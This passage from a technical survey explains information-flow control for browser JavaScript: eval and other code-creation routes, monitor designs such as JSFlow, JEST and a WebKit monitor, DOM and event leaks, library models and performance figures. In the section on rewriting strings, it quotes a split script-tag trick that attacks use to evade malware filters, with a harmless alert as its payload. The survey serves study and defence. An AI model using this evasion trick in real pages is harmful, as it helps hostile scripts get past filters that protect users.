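Monitors and multi-execution can handle code after it is created, which a purely static analysis can't do. They still need a rule for running text as code, because the text may depend on a secret and, once it runs, it can write to anything the script can reach.

### The routes from text to code

The best-known way for a script to create code while the page runs is `eval`, which parses a string as JavaScript and runs it immediately. The new code can use the local variables of the calling function if the script calls `eval` by its own name, but only global variables if the script calls it through another name.

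The `Function` constructor builds a function from strings, and `setTimeout` and `setInterval` accept a string of code to run later. A script can also insert a script element, change its text or address, or write a new one into the page with `document.write`. HTML attributes such as `onclick` also contain code as text.

Richards, Hammer and colleagues, in *The Eval that Men Do*, measured most of these routes in March 2011. They modified WebKit to record what scripts did and to save every string passed to `eval`. They used the 100 most popular websites by hand for one to five minutes each. An automated browser also visited the top 10,000 sites twice, once only loading the page for 30 seconds and once also clicking at random. In total, they recorded 550,358 calls to `eval`, with 337 MB of text.

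The table shows the share of sites that used each route at least once. In the last column, the lower figure is for visits without clicks and the higher one for visits with clicks.

| Route | Example | Top 100, by hand | Top 10,000, automated |
|---|---|---|---|
| `eval` by its own name | `eval("x = 4")` | 83% | 23–31% |
| `eval` by another name | `e = eval; e("x = 4")` | 10% | 1.3–1.6% |
| `Function` constructor | `Function("x", "print(x)")` | 49% | 8.8–13% |
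| `setTimeout` with a string | `setTimeout("callback()", 1000)` | 39% | 13–18% |
| Text of a script element | `s.text = "x = 4"` | 67% | 23–32% |
| Address of a script element | `s.src = "//host/a.js"` | 64% | 10–15% |
| `document.write` | `document.write("<script>...")` | 64% | 32–40% |

The paper's summary gives higher figures for `eval` on the 10,000 sites, 50% and 52%, without explaining the difference. For visits without clicks, it also reports 158,994 calls at an average of 34 per site, which implies about 4,700 sites and fits the higher figure.

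A system that handles only `eval` would miss most of the code created at runtime. On ask.com, 1.39 MB of the 2.22 MB of code arrived through one of these routes, but `eval` accounted for less than 4 KB. An advertising script on the site loaded further scripts, which loaded more.

Most of the strings passed to `eval` were short and simple. Between 22% and 37% contained data in JSON, a text format based on JavaScript's notation, or in a close variant. Many other calls were unnecessary. The German news site heute.de used `eval` in a loop to look up variables named `flash2Installed`, `flash3Installed` and so on, to recover a version number it had already stored. But more than 41% of the strings depended on the local variables around the call, so a browser couldn't simply run them in isolation.

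These figures describe the web of 2011, when JavaScript had only recently gained `JSON.parse`, a safe way to read JSON. *Eval begone!*, a follow-up to the study, describes a semi-automatic way to replace the common patterns with safer code.

### Analysing what is known and postponing the rest

Chugh and colleagues do as much of the analysis as possible statically. Their system analyses the available code and works out which checks any later code must pass. When that code arrives, the system performs these *residual checks*. If the new code loads more code, the process repeats.

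Suppose the loan page's own script copies the income into a global variable called `amount`, and the policy forbids advertising scripts from reading the income. The analysis of the page's script would find that `amount` also holds the income. The residual check on a new advertising script could then be whether it reads `amount`.

The project page describes the residual checks as syntactic, meaning they inspect the text of the new code without running it. Chugh and colleagues found that these checks were orders of magnitude faster on large real websites than checking all the code, so a visitor would hardly notice them.

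Bichhawat and colleagues point out that the method restricts the language, excluding the `with` statement and access to properties whose names the script computes. For example, the expression `window["am" + "ount"]` reads the variable `amount` without containing its name. A purely textual check must either reject all code that computes property names, including harmless code, or risk missing a leak.

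*Information Flow Analysis for a Dynamically Typed Functional Language with Staged Metaprogramming* (2013) presents a static analysis, with a proof of soundness, for a small language that has a more structured way of generating code than `eval`. This is a first step towards analysing JavaScript, but the proof doesn't cover the arbitrary strings that existing pages pass to `eval`.

### A secret that selects the code

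In this example, h is high and is either 0 or 1, and everything else starts low:

```
l = 0;
texts = ["l = 1", "l = 2"];
eval(texts[h]);
```

Without protection, l is set to 1 if h is 0 and to 2 if h is 1. The leak comes entirely from the choice of string, because the script contains no `if`, neither string contains a secret, and the new code only assigns a public constant.

JSFlow handles the last line as follows:

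1. It reads `texts[h]`. The label of the result includes the label of h, so the string is high.
2. It parses the string into a program.
3. It raises the pc for the new program to the old pc ⊔ the label of the string.
4. It runs the program. The assignment writes to a low variable under a high pc, so the no-sensitive-upgrade rule stops the script.

JSFlow treats a function the same way when its selection depends on a secret. Here it stops the script for both values of h, so stopping reveals nothing about h. If the first line were `l = upg 0 to h`, the script could finish, and l would be high.

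The rule restricts `eval` more than ordinary code in one respect. If x is low, a script may run `x = income`, which makes x high. But `eval("x = " + income)` performs the assignment under a high pc, so JSFlow stops it. A script can avoid this by keeping the assignment outside `eval`, as in `x = eval(income)`, if the interpreter gives the result the string's label.

Richards and colleagues call this second form the standard way to read JSON with `eval`, but they also found scripts that put the assignment inside the string, such as Ask.com's `eval("var p=" + str + ";")`. If `str` contained secret data, a harmless script written this way could cause a false stop.

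In their WebKit monitor, Bichhawat and colleagues adopt the existing treatment of `eval`. However, if `l` is a local variable, their deferred check can let the script run past the assignment.

### Why earlier branch endpoints stay valid

The WebKit monitor has a further problem to solve, because it decides where a branch ends from a graph of all the possible jumps. Code that arrives later isn't in that graph:

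```
if (h) { eval(text); }
l = 0;
```

When the script tests `h`, the monitor raises the pc and records `l = 0` as the point where it may lower the pc again. It does this before it has processed the code in `text`. If that code could jump past `l = 0`, this endpoint would be wrong, and the monitor would lower the pc too early.

WebKit compiles the code passed to `eval` as a separate block, much like the body of a function, and the monitor builds a separate graph for that block. A `break` in the new code can't end a loop outside it, and a `return` can't end the function that called `eval`, because JavaScript rejects both as syntax errors. When the new code finishes normally, control returns to the instruction after the call.

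An exception can still end the block early, but the original graph already accounts for this because the monitor treats a call to `eval`, like a function call, as an instruction that may throw. The new graph therefore adds its own branches and endpoints without moving any earlier ones.

Compiling at runtime could also leak information through the compiler. If WebKit's compiler used the page's secret data, it might produce different instructions for the same text. Bichhawat and colleagues therefore assume that the compiler's output depends only on the program and the functions currently running, not on the objects in memory, and they report that the real compiler works this way.

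### Rewriting each string before it runs

An inlined monitor has no control over the engine's parser, so it must rewrite the text before the browser receives it. Magazinius and colleagues introduced this for strings whose content may be unknown until runtime. With shadow variables, where true stands for high, the call `eval(text)` becomes roughly:

```
saved = pc;
pc = pc || shadow.text;
eval(rewrite(text));
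pc = saved;
```

The second line raises the pc if the string is secret, as JSFlow does. In the example with two strings, `rewrite` adds the usual check to `l = 1` or `l = 2`, and the check fails because the pc is high. `rewrite` also transforms any call to `eval` inside the new code, so code created by nested calls is checked too.

The function `rewrite` must therefore be available for as long as the page runs. This is simple if it is written in JavaScript. Chudnov and Naumann wrote JEST's rewriter in Haskell, which browsers don't run, so JEST sends each string to a proxy server for rewriting. This works when a proxy already delivers the page, but a website that included JEST directly would need a JavaScript version of the rewriter. Chudnov and Naumann suggest compiling the Haskell code to JavaScript.

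Script elements are harder to rewrite than `eval` strings because a page can assemble them from pieces. Richards and colleagues give an example typical of attacks that try to get past malware filters:

```
<script>document.write("<scr");</script>
ipt>alert("this is malicious");</script>
```

The first line writes `<scr` into the page, directly before the text `ipt>`, and together they form the opening tag of a new script element. A rewriter that checks only the string passed to `document.write` finds no script there, and one that checks only the original HTML treats the second line as ordinary text. To catch the script, a rewriter would have to track how the browser combines the pieces. A monitor inside the engine avoids this problem because it receives the finished script from the browser.

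### Separate runs with separate strings

Secure multi-execution needs no label on the string. In the example with two strings, suppose the default value of h is 0 and its real value is 1. The low run evaluates `l = 1` and the high run evaluates `l = 2`, each with its own copy of l. If the script then sends l to a server, the low run sends 1 whatever the real value of h is.

The two runs now execute different programs. This is safe, but a poorly chosen default can crash the low run in another way. If the default income is an empty string, the low run's call to `eval("x = " + income)` evaluates the incomplete statement `x = `, which is a syntax error. A default of 0 would avoid this.

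Inserted script elements also behave differently from `eval`, because both runs in FlowFox share one DOM. Inserting an element is a low call unless the policy assigns it another level, so only the low run inserts its script. This protects the secret, but if a page builds a script element from secret data, the inserted script is based on the default value instead.

Faceted values lead to much the same result as separate runs. If h is ⟨k ? 1 : 0⟩, then `texts[h]` is ⟨k ? "l = 2" : "l = 1"⟩. The interpreter has to evaluate each string in its own view, and l becomes ⟨k ? 2 : 1⟩.

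### A variable that exists only if a secret is true

Code passed to `eval` can also change what the existing code does. Hedin and colleagues give an example in which `eval` declares a variable. It is slightly extended here with a global variable l that starts as a public 1:

```
l = 1;
function f(x) {
  if (h) { eval("var l"); }
  l = 0;
}
f();
```

If h is true, `eval` creates a local variable l inside the function. The assignment `l = 0` then changes the local l, and the global l stays 1. If h is false, no local l exists, and the same assignment changes the global l to 0. The assignment is outside the branch, so the pc is low in both cases.

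JavaScript moves every ordinary `var` declaration to the start of its function, so `if (h) { var l; }` creates the local variable whether or not `h` is true. If the declaration is in a string passed to `eval` inside the branch, JavaScript doesn't process it until the branch runs, so the variable is created only when `h` is true.

JSFlow treats a function's local variables as properties of an object, so declaring `l` under a high pc requires that object's structure label to be high. The label is low here, so JSFlow stops the script at the `eval` when `h` is true.

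The annotation `upgv x to h` at the start of the function raises the structure label of the object that holds x, and so of all the function's local variables. The script may then declare l. If h is false, JSFlow blocks the write to the global l, as in the earlier `with` example.

| Enforcement | h is true | h is false |
|---|---|---|
| None | Global l stays 1 | Global l becomes 0 |
| JSFlow | Stops at the `eval` | Global l becomes 0 |
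| JSFlow with `upgv x to h` | Global l stays 1 | Stops at `l = 0` |
| JEST | Blocks the `eval` | Global l becomes 0 |
| Low run of multi-execution, with false as the default for h | Global l becomes 0 | Global l becomes 0 |

In JSFlow and JEST, only the termination channel remains. The low run of multi-execution does the same thing in both cases.

Chudnov and Naumann use a simpler rule in JEST, which forbids evaluated code to declare new variables under a high pc. They show that the existence of a variable can leak a secret even if the script never writes to it:

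```
public = 1;
if (secret) eval("var x;");
try { x; } catch (e) { public = 0; }
```

Reading a variable that doesn't exist throws an exception, so `public` ends up as 0 only if `secret` is false. JEST's rule blocks the declaration, and no annotation can allow it. This probably causes few false stops, because Richards and colleagues found only a few sites that declared variables inside `eval`. The problem also arises only when `eval` is called by its own name, since code from the other routes runs in the global scope.

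### Public text from an untrusted author

All these rules limit what new code can reveal. They don't check whether the code does what the visitor wanted.

Suppose the loan page downloads its interest formula as text from a partner company and passes it to `eval`. An attacker who controls the partner's server replaces the formula with one that uses an interest rate of 2% instead of 5%. The text isn't secret, so JSFlow runs it under a low pc. The new code can't send the income to the attacker, but it can show the visitor a false instalment.

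To prevent this, the text needs an *integrity label*, which records whether an untrusted party has influenced it. This label can spread through a program by the same rules as a secrecy label. Chudnov and Naumann note that a higher label can mean more secret, less trustworthy or both. If the partner's text carried an "untrusted" label, `eval` would raise the pc to "untrusted", and the monitor would stop the new code before it changed the trusted instalment.

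Most policies for these systems label data only by secrecy. Jang and colleagues' rule against location hijacking is an exception, because it labels data from third-party code as untrusted. Browser vendors later took a more direct approach with Content Security Policy and Trusted Types, which restrict which text may become code.

Richards and colleagues tagged each string with its source, such as a constant in a script, the DOM, a server's reply, a cookie or a form field. These tags were close to integrity labels. On the sites they used by hand, about half of the evaluated strings were built entirely from constants or pieces of them. In the automated visits, strings from the DOM were as common as constants. A rule that allowed `eval` only on constants would therefore have broken many pages.

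The tags could also mislead. Google sent much of its data as a constant string inside a new script element, because the same-origin policy blocked an ordinary request to the server that held the data. The tool classed this string as a constant, although it had just arrived from a server. An integrity label would have to record which server supplied the script, not just whether the string was fixed within it.

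Even a correct integrity label identifies only who influenced the code. If the lender's own programmer types the wrong interest rate into the formula, the code is fully trusted but computes the wrong instalment.

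## Covering the DOM, built-in libraries and events

Scripts do much of their work by calling functions that the browser provides, which are usually native code, compiled into the browser, instead of JavaScript. A monitor can carry labels correctly through every statement of a script and still lose them in such a call:

```
l = h.toLowerCase();
```

The native function takes a plain string and returns a plain string. If the monitor passes it the text of the secret h and labels the result public, the script gets a public copy of h. Giving every result the combined label of the function's arguments is safer, but this rule also fails if a function stores data between calls or calls back into the script.

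The monitor therefore needs a *library model*, a description of how labels pass through a function whose code it can't track. The developers of JSFlow wrote such models by hand for the whole standard library. They could have rewritten many of the functions in JavaScript, but a script can't send a request to the operating system or the browser without calling native code.

### Shallow and deep models

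In simplified form, JSFlow's model of `toLowerCase` is:

```
function toLowerCase(x) {
  var s = toStringValue(x);
  return labeled(s.value.toLowerCase(), s.label);
}
```

The first line uses JSFlow's own string conversion, so that any script functions the conversion calls run under the right pc. The second line calls the browser's function on the text without its label, then gives the result the input's label. Hedin and colleagues call this a *shallow model* because it uses only the labels of the input and output.

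A shallow model isn't enough for `every`, an array function that runs a test on each element in turn and stops at the first one that fails:

```
l = false;
list = [h];
Object.defineProperty(list, 1, {
  get: function () { l = true; return 1; }
});
list.every(function (item) { return item; });
```

The test here returns the element itself. The array has a secret, h, in position 0 and a *getter* in position 1, a function that JavaScript runs whenever something reads that position. If h is false, `every` stops after the first element. Otherwise it reads the second, and the getter sets l to true.

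Labeling the result of `every` wouldn't help, because the script ignores the result. The write to l happens during the call, and the branch that leads to it is inside the native function. JSFlow therefore uses a *deep model*, which repeats part of the function's own work. Its main loop is roughly:

```
while (k < length) {
  var result = toBoolean(test(get(k)));
  raisePC(result.label);
  label = combine(label, result.label);
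  if (!result.value) { popPC(); return labeled(false, label); }
  k = k + 1;
}
```

After the test on the first element, the pc is high because the result depends on h. If h is true, the loop reads position 1, and JSFlow stops the script when the getter tries to write to l. If h is false, the function returns a high false, and l stays false. Elements before the first secret one are still read under a low pc, so getters and tests may write public data there.

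Models make up 30% of JSFlow's code, and they cover only the standard library. Hedin and colleagues expect that covering all the browser's functions would increase this share significantly. Each model also depends on its author's understanding of the real function, and any mismatch between the model and the function could leak a secret.

The printed model of `slice`, which cuts a piece out of a string, contains such a mismatch. A script may pass objects as the start and end positions, and JavaScript then calls the script's functions to convert them to numbers. The printed code converts the start position but ignores the resulting number and its label, and passes the original object to the native function. This mistake may be only in the printed version, but it is easy to overlook in a function of about 20 lines.

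### Collections that change by themselves

The DOM is harder to model because a change to one element can affect what a script reads somewhere else. Suppose a page contains one `div` element with both the id and the name "A":

```
c = document.getElementsByName("A");
if (h) { document.getElementById("A").name = "B"; }
l = c.length;
```

The first line returns a *live collection*, a list that the browser updates as the page changes. It starts with one element. If h is true, the script renames that element and the length drops to 0, which leaks h even though the script never writes to c.

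In JSFlow, every DOM node keeps a table of searches, such as the search for the name "A". Each search has a label for how the nodes below affect it. If the document's table labels this search public, JSFlow stops the script when it tries to rename the element under a high pc. If the label is secret, the script may rename the element, but the length of c is then secret whether h is true or false.

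Rajani and colleagues, who extended the WebKit monitor to the DOM and to events, found they needed no labels for searches. WebKit marks a live collection as out of date whenever the page changes and searches the page again when a script next reads the collection's length. Their monitor labels each field of a node, including its name and its links to other nodes, and the search combines the labels of the fields it reads. A script can rename an element under a high pc only if the name field is already high. The search then reads that field, so the length is high too.

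They contrast this with JSFlow and with Almeida Matos, Fragoso Santos and Rezk's monitor in *An Information Flow Monitor for a Core of DOM*. They write that both require the programmer to supply a label for each kind of element that a script might search for. But the automatic method can be less precise. If one link in the page is secret because it may lead to an extra `div`, a search for images has to follow the same link, so the number of images also becomes secret, even though the `div` can't affect it.

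Some properties expose data that is stored elsewhere. A form, for instance, has properties that give access to the fields inside it, so a script on the loan page could reach the income through the form instead of the income field. An element's attributes are separate nodes, but they can also appear as properties of the element. If a model simply read such a property from the browser, it could return a secret without its label, so it has to determine where the browser stores the data and use the label from there.

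### How an event reaches its handlers

When a visitor clicks a button, the browser may run handlers on the button and on every element that contains it. The button is the event's *target*, and the *propagation path* runs from the target up to the root of the page. The browser works through the path in three phases:

1. In the *capture phase*, it goes from the root down to the target's parent.
2. In the *target phase*, it runs the handlers on the target itself.
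3. In the *bubble phase*, it goes from the target's parent back up to the root.

A script chooses between the capture and bubble phases when it registers a handler. The browser determines the event's path through the DOM before it runs the first handler, and the path does not change if a handler moves elements.

The path can reveal a secret, as in this version of an example from Rajani and colleagues:

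```
l = false;
a.addEventListener("click", function () { l = true; }, true);
if (h) { a.appendChild(b); }
b.click();
```

The second line registers a handler on element a for the capture phase. If h is true, the script places b inside a, so the click on b also runs the handler on a, which sets l to true. If h is false, b is outside a, and the handler doesn't run. The write to l is not inside any branch on h.

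To prevent this, the monitor starts each handler with the following pc:

pc = label of the event ⊔ labels of the links on the path ⊔ label of the handler ⊔ pc when the script registered the handler

If a script triggers the event, as here, the event's label is the pc at that moment. If the visitor triggers it, the monitor uses the labels of the event and its target. The last part of the formula covers handlers that a script registers only if a secret is true.

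In the example, when the pc is high, the script can place b inside a only if the fields that link the two elements are already high. The handler on a then runs under a high pc, and the monitor blocks the write to l.

The monitor applies the label of the whole path to every handler for the event. A handler on b would therefore also run under a high pc, even though it runs whether or not b is inside a. This is safe, but the monitor may stop programs that leak nothing.

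### A handler that waits at an alert box

Rajani and colleagues found that a browser can start one event handler before another has finished, contrary to an assumption in earlier work on browsers. On Chrome 40, they clicked a paragraph whose handler opened an alert box, and then resized the window before closing the box. Chrome ran the resize handler while the click handler was still waiting.

The second handler can therefore observe a state that the first one meant to be temporary:

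```
function first() {
  l = true;
  if (h) { alert("Please confirm"); }
  l = false;
}
function second() { c = l; }
```

Suppose the events for both handlers have already occurred and `first` is running. If h is true, `first` waits at the alert box while `second` copies true into c. If h is false, no box appears, so `second` runs after `first` has finished and copies false into c, which means c ends up equal to h in both cases.

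It might seem enough to run `second` under the high pc of the branch that opened the alert box. If c starts low, the no-sensitive-upgrade rule then blocks the write. But if c starts high, the monitor allows it, and the result depends on h:

| h | When `second` runs | c afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| true | During the alert box, under a high pc | true, high |
| false | After `first`, under a low pc | false, low |

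An attacker can learn h by checking whether c is readable as public data, because c is readable exactly when h is false.

The monitor instead delays `second`. While a handler is waiting under a high pc, the browser may start another event only if that event's label is at least as high as that pc. The event for `second` is public, so it waits until `first` has finished, and `c` becomes false with a low label, whatever `h` is. The delay could still reveal `h` to someone who measures time, but the guarantee doesn't cover timing.

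Browsers differ in which calls can suspend a handler. Rajani and colleagues therefore left the list of such calls unspecified in their formal model, which keeps a stack of the events that the browser has started but not finished. They proved noninterference for terminating runs whichever calls are on the list, but anyone applying the model to a real browser still has to find all the calls that can suspend a handler there.

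### A leak through a lookup table

The DOM standard doesn't specify which element `getElementById` should return if several elements have the same id. Rajani and colleagues read WebKit's source code to settle such questions, and found further leaks caused by its optimisations.

WebKit keeps a table that maps ids to elements, so that it doesn't have to search the whole page for each lookup. The table contains only some of the elements, and if an id is missing from it, WebKit searches the page. In the next example, only a is part of the page at first, and all the fields of b are high:

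```
c.setAttribute("id", "x1");
if (h) { b.appendChild(c); }
a.appendChild(b);
r = document.getElementById("x1");
```

The third line adds b to the page, together with c if h is true. This line runs under a low pc, so an obvious rule would give any new table entries a low label.

If h is true, the last line finds c in the table and returns it with a low label. If h is false, the table has no entry for "x1", so WebKit searches the page. The search passes through b, whose fields are high, and returns a high `null`, meaning no such element exists. The script can distinguish the two results by whether r is public.

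The label of c's table entry must therefore include the labels of all the links from b to c. The link from b to c is high, so the entry is high, and r is high in both cases. The DOM standard doesn't mention the table, so a developer who worked only from the standard would have missed this leak.

Rajani and colleagues added their checks to the native code for all DOM functions up to Level 3, the version that most browsers then supported. They also covered the built-in functions for arrays, strings and regular expressions. This added about 2,300 lines of code to the original monitor's 4,500. The checks use the browser's own data structures, so unlike JSFlow's deep models, they don't need a separate copy of each function. But the proof covers a formal model of the DOM, not WebKit's own code, and a new optimisation in WebKit could create a leak that the model doesn't include.

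### Models that fit on one line

The set of functions to cover also keeps growing. Fragoso Santos, Rezk and Almeida Matos (2015), in *Modular Monitor Extensions for Information Flow Security in JavaScript*, call the behaviour of browser functions a moving target. Their system lets developers extend the monitor for each new group of functions, even at runtime. The extension they supplied covers only part of the first version of the DOM, so somebody would have to write the others.

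Hedin, Sjösten and colleagues (2017), in *A Principled Approach to Tracking Information Flow in the Presence of Libraries*, tried to make each model much shorter. Their models state only how the label of the result depends on the labels of the inputs. In slightly adapted notation, with + for combining labels, three of them are:

```
min    :: a b  -> a + b
length :: [a]s -> s
sum    :: [a]s -> a + s
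```

When a script calls `min`, the monitor removes the two arguments' labels and stores these labels as a and b. The library function runs on the unlabeled values, and the monitor labels the result a + b. For a list, a stands for the labels of the elements and s for the label of the list's structure. The length of a list depends only on its structure, while the sum also depends on its elements. A script may therefore learn how many secret numbers a list contains if the structure is public.

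The monitor passes the library a wrapper around a large object and removes the label of each part only when the library reads it. Removing every label before each call would be slow and could give the result a more secret label than necessary. If a function reads only the first three elements of a list, a secret in the tenth doesn't affect the result's label.

Functions that a script passes to a library need wrappers too. When the library calls such a function, the wrapper adds labels to the arguments and removes the label from the result. The wrapper may not have the right labels when the script passes the function, because the library can store the function and call it later with other data. The wrapper therefore carries only a name, and the model of the library function that makes the call defines the labels for that name.

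The 2017 models can't describe a library that changes its own state. Sjösten, Hedin and Sabelfeld (2018), in *Information Flow Tracking for Side-effectful Libraries*, added a separate area of memory, the *model heap*, which holds labels for that state between calls. They tried it on a model of a file-system library similar to the one in Node.js, a system for running JavaScript on servers. Their model for deleting a folder is:

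```
rmdirSync :: a -> l + a {| l <- a |}
```

Here a is the label of the folder's path and l is the label of the file system's state. The part in braces passes the path's label on to the state, because a deletion changes what later calls will find. The result reports whether the deletion succeeded, so it depends on both the path and the state. For brevity, the example uses one label for the entire file system, so deleting one folder with a secret path can make the results of later deletions secret too.

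The programmer still has to work out what each function does to the state. In another example, Sjösten and colleagues model a library that stores a single value. When a script replaces a secret value with a public one, the state can safely become public again. But in a file system, deleting a public folder doesn't undo an earlier deletion of a secret one. Both models nevertheless use the same update, `l <- a`. If the arrow replaces the old label, the file-system model can leak which folder the script deleted earlier, but if it combines the old label with the new one, the single-value model is stricter than necessary.

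The researchers built both systems for small research languages and left integration into JSFlow for later. Sjösten and colleagues checked their proof of noninterference in Coq, but the proof assumes that every library model is correct, and the monitor can't detect an incorrect model while a script runs. If a programmer wrote the model `min :: a b -> a` by mistake, a script could call `min(1, h)`, where h is a secret 0 or 1, and get back the value of h labeled public.

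## Measuring the slowdown

All of these systems slow scripts down, with published figures ranging from about 5% longer to 1,680 times as long. The researchers tested different programs against different baselines, so the smallest figure doesn't necessarily belong to the fastest browser.

### The published figures

CrowdFlow, one of the systems in the table below, reduces the slowdown by tracking fully only part of the time. This version of WebKit, which Kerschbaumer, Hennigan and colleagues describe in *CrowdFlow*, normally follows only direct copies, but at each function call it has a 5% chance of switching to fuller tracking.

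The percentages are the extra running time, so 100% means that a script takes twice as long. In the last column, "partial" means that the system covers only what a script reveals through branches that run, and "full" means that it also covers what a script reveals by not taking a branch.

| System | Date | Workload | Baseline | Extra time | Implicit flows |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Jang and colleagues | 2010 | Page visits | Original scripts | 110–690% | Partial |
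| Just and colleagues | 2011 | V8 suite | Interpreter | 100–200% | Full, except exceptions |
| FlowFox | 2012 | V8 suite | Unmodified engine | About 100% | Full |
| FlowFox | 2012 | Six browsing scenarios | Unmodified Firefox | About 20% | Full |
| Faceted values | 2012 | Hashing program, one to eight principals | One ordinary run in the same interpreter | 27–124% | Full |
| Labels in WebKit's interpreter | 2013 | SunSpider | Interpreter | 83% | Partial |
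| Labels in WebKit's JIT compiler | 2013 | SunSpider, V8 and Kraken | JIT compiler | 73% | Partial |
| CrowdFlow | 2013 | SunSpider and V8 | Interpreter | 28–32% | Partial, in sampled calls |
| JSFlow | 2014 | Overall estimate | Engine with JIT | About 100 times as long | Full |
| WebKit monitor, basic | 2014 | SunSpider | Interpreter | 121% | Full |
| WebKit monitor, optimised | 2014 | SunSpider | Interpreter | 45% | Full |
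| WebKit monitor, both versions | 2014 | Nine websites | Interpreter | About 29% | Full |
| WebKit monitor with DOM | 2015 | Dromaeo | Interpreter | 71% | Full |
| WebKit monitor with DOM | 2015 | Ten websites | Interpreter | About 32% | Full |
| JEST | 2015 | Selected SunSpider and Kraken tests | Node.js with JIT | 8 to 364 times as long | Full |

SunSpider, V8 and Kraken are collections of small, computation-heavy test programs, and Dromaeo tests DOM functions. The figures for the first two systems come from an overview by Kerschbaumer and colleagues. Those for faceted values are derived from the timings in the section on multi-execution, where one ordinary run took 274 seconds.

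Some papers report a doubled running time as an overhead of 200% instead of 100%. De Groef and colleagues found that FlowFox roughly doubled the running time of the V8 suite. The overview lists this overhead as about 200%, although the same paper describes it elsewhere as a doubling.

De Groef and colleagues also measured memory. Just after loading, FlowFox used 88% more than Firefox on average across 500 websites.

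### A 100-millisecond script

Most of the WebKit figures compare a tracking interpreter with an ordinary interpreter, because the researchers switched off the JIT compiler. They therefore don't measure the slowdown a user would see relative to a normal browser, which runs with the JIT compiler on.

Kerschbaumer and colleagues published enough timings to convert several of their figures to a common baseline. Suppose a script takes 100 milliseconds with WebKit's JIT compiler and slows down by as much as the SunSpider suite does overall:

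| Version of WebKit | Published overhead | Time for the script |
|---|---|---|
| JIT compiler, no tracking | – | 100 ms |
| JIT compiler with labels | 74% over the JIT compiler | 174 ms |
| Interpreter, no tracking | – | 349 ms |
| CrowdFlow | 28% over the interpreter | 446 ms |
| Interpreter with 64-bit labels | 83% over the interpreter | 636 ms |
| Interpreter with 16-bit labels | 138% over the interpreter | 828 ms |

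CrowdFlow has the lowest percentage slowdown but takes more than twice as long as the JIT compiler with labels. Its time in the table is calculated as 349 ms × 1.28, because its paper compares it only with the interpreter. The comparison is reasonable, since the researchers used the same model of computer for all these tests and the ordinary interpreter's SunSpider totals in the two papers differ by only 1%.

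Kerschbaumer and colleagues report that the interpreter with 64-bit labels has an overhead of 83% against the interpreter without labels and 536% against the JIT compiler.

WebKit had a simple JIT compiler and an optimising one, and Kerschbaumer and colleagues added labels only to the simple one. They measured the 74% slowdown against the same simple compiler without labels, not against WebKit at its fastest. They also ran each suite once before timing it, which left out the compilation time that a visitor opening a page for the first time would have to wait for.

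Bichhawat and colleagues timed the scripts that run when nine popular sites load, including Google, Amazon and Wikipedia, and found that the ordinary browser was slightly slower with the JIT compiler than without it. Compiling code takes time, and a short script may finish before the faster code makes up for that time. The interpreter was therefore a fair baseline for page loading in 2014, but not for long computations.

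### The choice of test program

The average for a suite can hide large differences between programs. With labels in the JIT compiler, a test that makes many recursive calls took 346% longer, while one that searches DNA sequences with regular expressions took no longer. The system updates its record of the pc at each function call, condition and loop, but regular expressions run mostly in native code, where it has nothing to update.

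A monitor can have low overhead because its tracking is incomplete. The 2014 version of the WebKit monitor had almost no overhead on SunSpider's regular expression test, but it didn't yet track data through native code. A later version with that tracking would probably be slower on this test.

The effect of an optimisation also depends on the test. The optimised WebKit monitor initially gives all of a function's local variables the label of the pc. It labels them individually only after the function reads from an object with a different label. This reduced the overhead on SunSpider from 121% to 45%, but on the nine websites the overhead was about 29% with or without the optimisation. Bichhawat and colleagues infer that real scripts read from objects more often than SunSpider's programs do.

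They also ran JSBench, a suite built from the code of real websites, and both versions had an overhead of about 38%. This supports the website result and suggests that the optimisation helps real websites less than it helps SunSpider.

Kerschbaumer and colleagues tested their DOM tracking with the Dromaeo benchmark and measured an overhead of 5%. Rajani and colleagues measured 71% for theirs on the same benchmark. Both groups compared their systems with WebKit's ordinary interpreter. Kerschbaumer's system labels page elements and their attributes by origin, while Rajani's does much more checking. The extra checks probably account for much of the gap, although the groups also used different computers and versions of WebKit.

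FlowFox doubled the running time of the V8 benchmark suite but added almost nothing to a test in which each input or output took 10 milliseconds. Its two runs of a script share each browser call, so only the computation doubles.

### Interpreters and rewritten scripts

JSFlow's developers estimate that it is about a hundred times slower than an engine with a JIT compiler. Much of the slowdown comes from the extra layer of interpretation, but removing that layer may not help much. Chudnov and Naumann mention an experiment in which Thiemann specialised JSFlow for a particular script, in effect compiling the script, and found that it ran only 1.8 times faster.

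JEST has no extra interpreter, but its rewritten scripts are still slow. On a SunSpider test that builds binary trees, the running time rose from 2.7 to 927 milliseconds, a factor of 342. A faster mode that follows the original script's behaviour less faithfully reduced the factor to 231. On a Kraken test that parses financial data in JSON, the factor was only eight.

Chudnov and Naumann used a different method to compare JEST with JSFlow. They timed a single run of a benchmark from start to finish, including Node.js's startup time. By this measure, JEST took 15.6 times as long as the original program and JSFlow took 1,680 times as long.

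Including the start-up time can make a slowdown look much smaller. If Node.js took 60 milliseconds to start, the binary-tree test would take about 63 milliseconds without JEST and 987 with it, so a 342-fold slowdown would appear to be about 16-fold. JEST's result of 15.6 is therefore consistent with the much higher factors in the other tests.

Chudnov and Naumann consider their benchmarks a worst case because the programs do far more computation than typical web applications. They also criticise related work for using website tests that are hard to reproduce, or baselines without a JIT compiler. Both criticisms are fair, but their own tests don't show how long a visitor would wait for a real page. JSBench would have been closer to real pages, but they rejected it because it relies heavily on `eval`, which complicated their measurements.

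### Less protection for less time

CrowdFlow saves time by tracking only a sample of function calls, so it misses some leaks. On SunSpider, it took 172% longer than the ordinary interpreter with full tracking always on, and 28% longer when it sampled 5% of calls. This is a reduction in overhead by a factor of about six, although the paper's abstract describes the improvement as an order of magnitude.

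CrowdFlow is designed to protect visitors as a group. When a browser detects a suspicious flow, it reports the flow to an outside service but doesn't stop the data from leaving. The service can then warn other users about the address that received the data.

To test CrowdFlow, the researchers had a program visit 500 popular websites as five separate users. Full tracking had found 8,764 suspicious flows on these sites. The first user found 5,480 of them, or 63%, and all five together found 8,716, or 99%.

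This could work against an attack on a popular site, but it would do little to protect someone who is an attacker's only target. The researchers say CrowdFlow isn't designed for targeted attacks. They also expect attackers to learn to detect when full tracking is off and send data only then. Full tracking also misses information revealed by branches that don't run, so the 99% isn't a share of all possible leaks.

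### Scripts that should have stopped

For their timing tests, both Bichhawat and colleagues and Rajani and colleagues made the WebKit monitor ignore violations and let every script continue.

Letting scripts run without stopping them is a sensible way to measure the overhead of tracking. If the monitor had stopped a 100-millisecond script after 20 milliseconds, the page would have seemed faster with tracking than without it. But the 29% and 32% overheads are for a browser that tracks data without protecting it, and they don't measure how many of the websites would still have worked with enforcement switched on.

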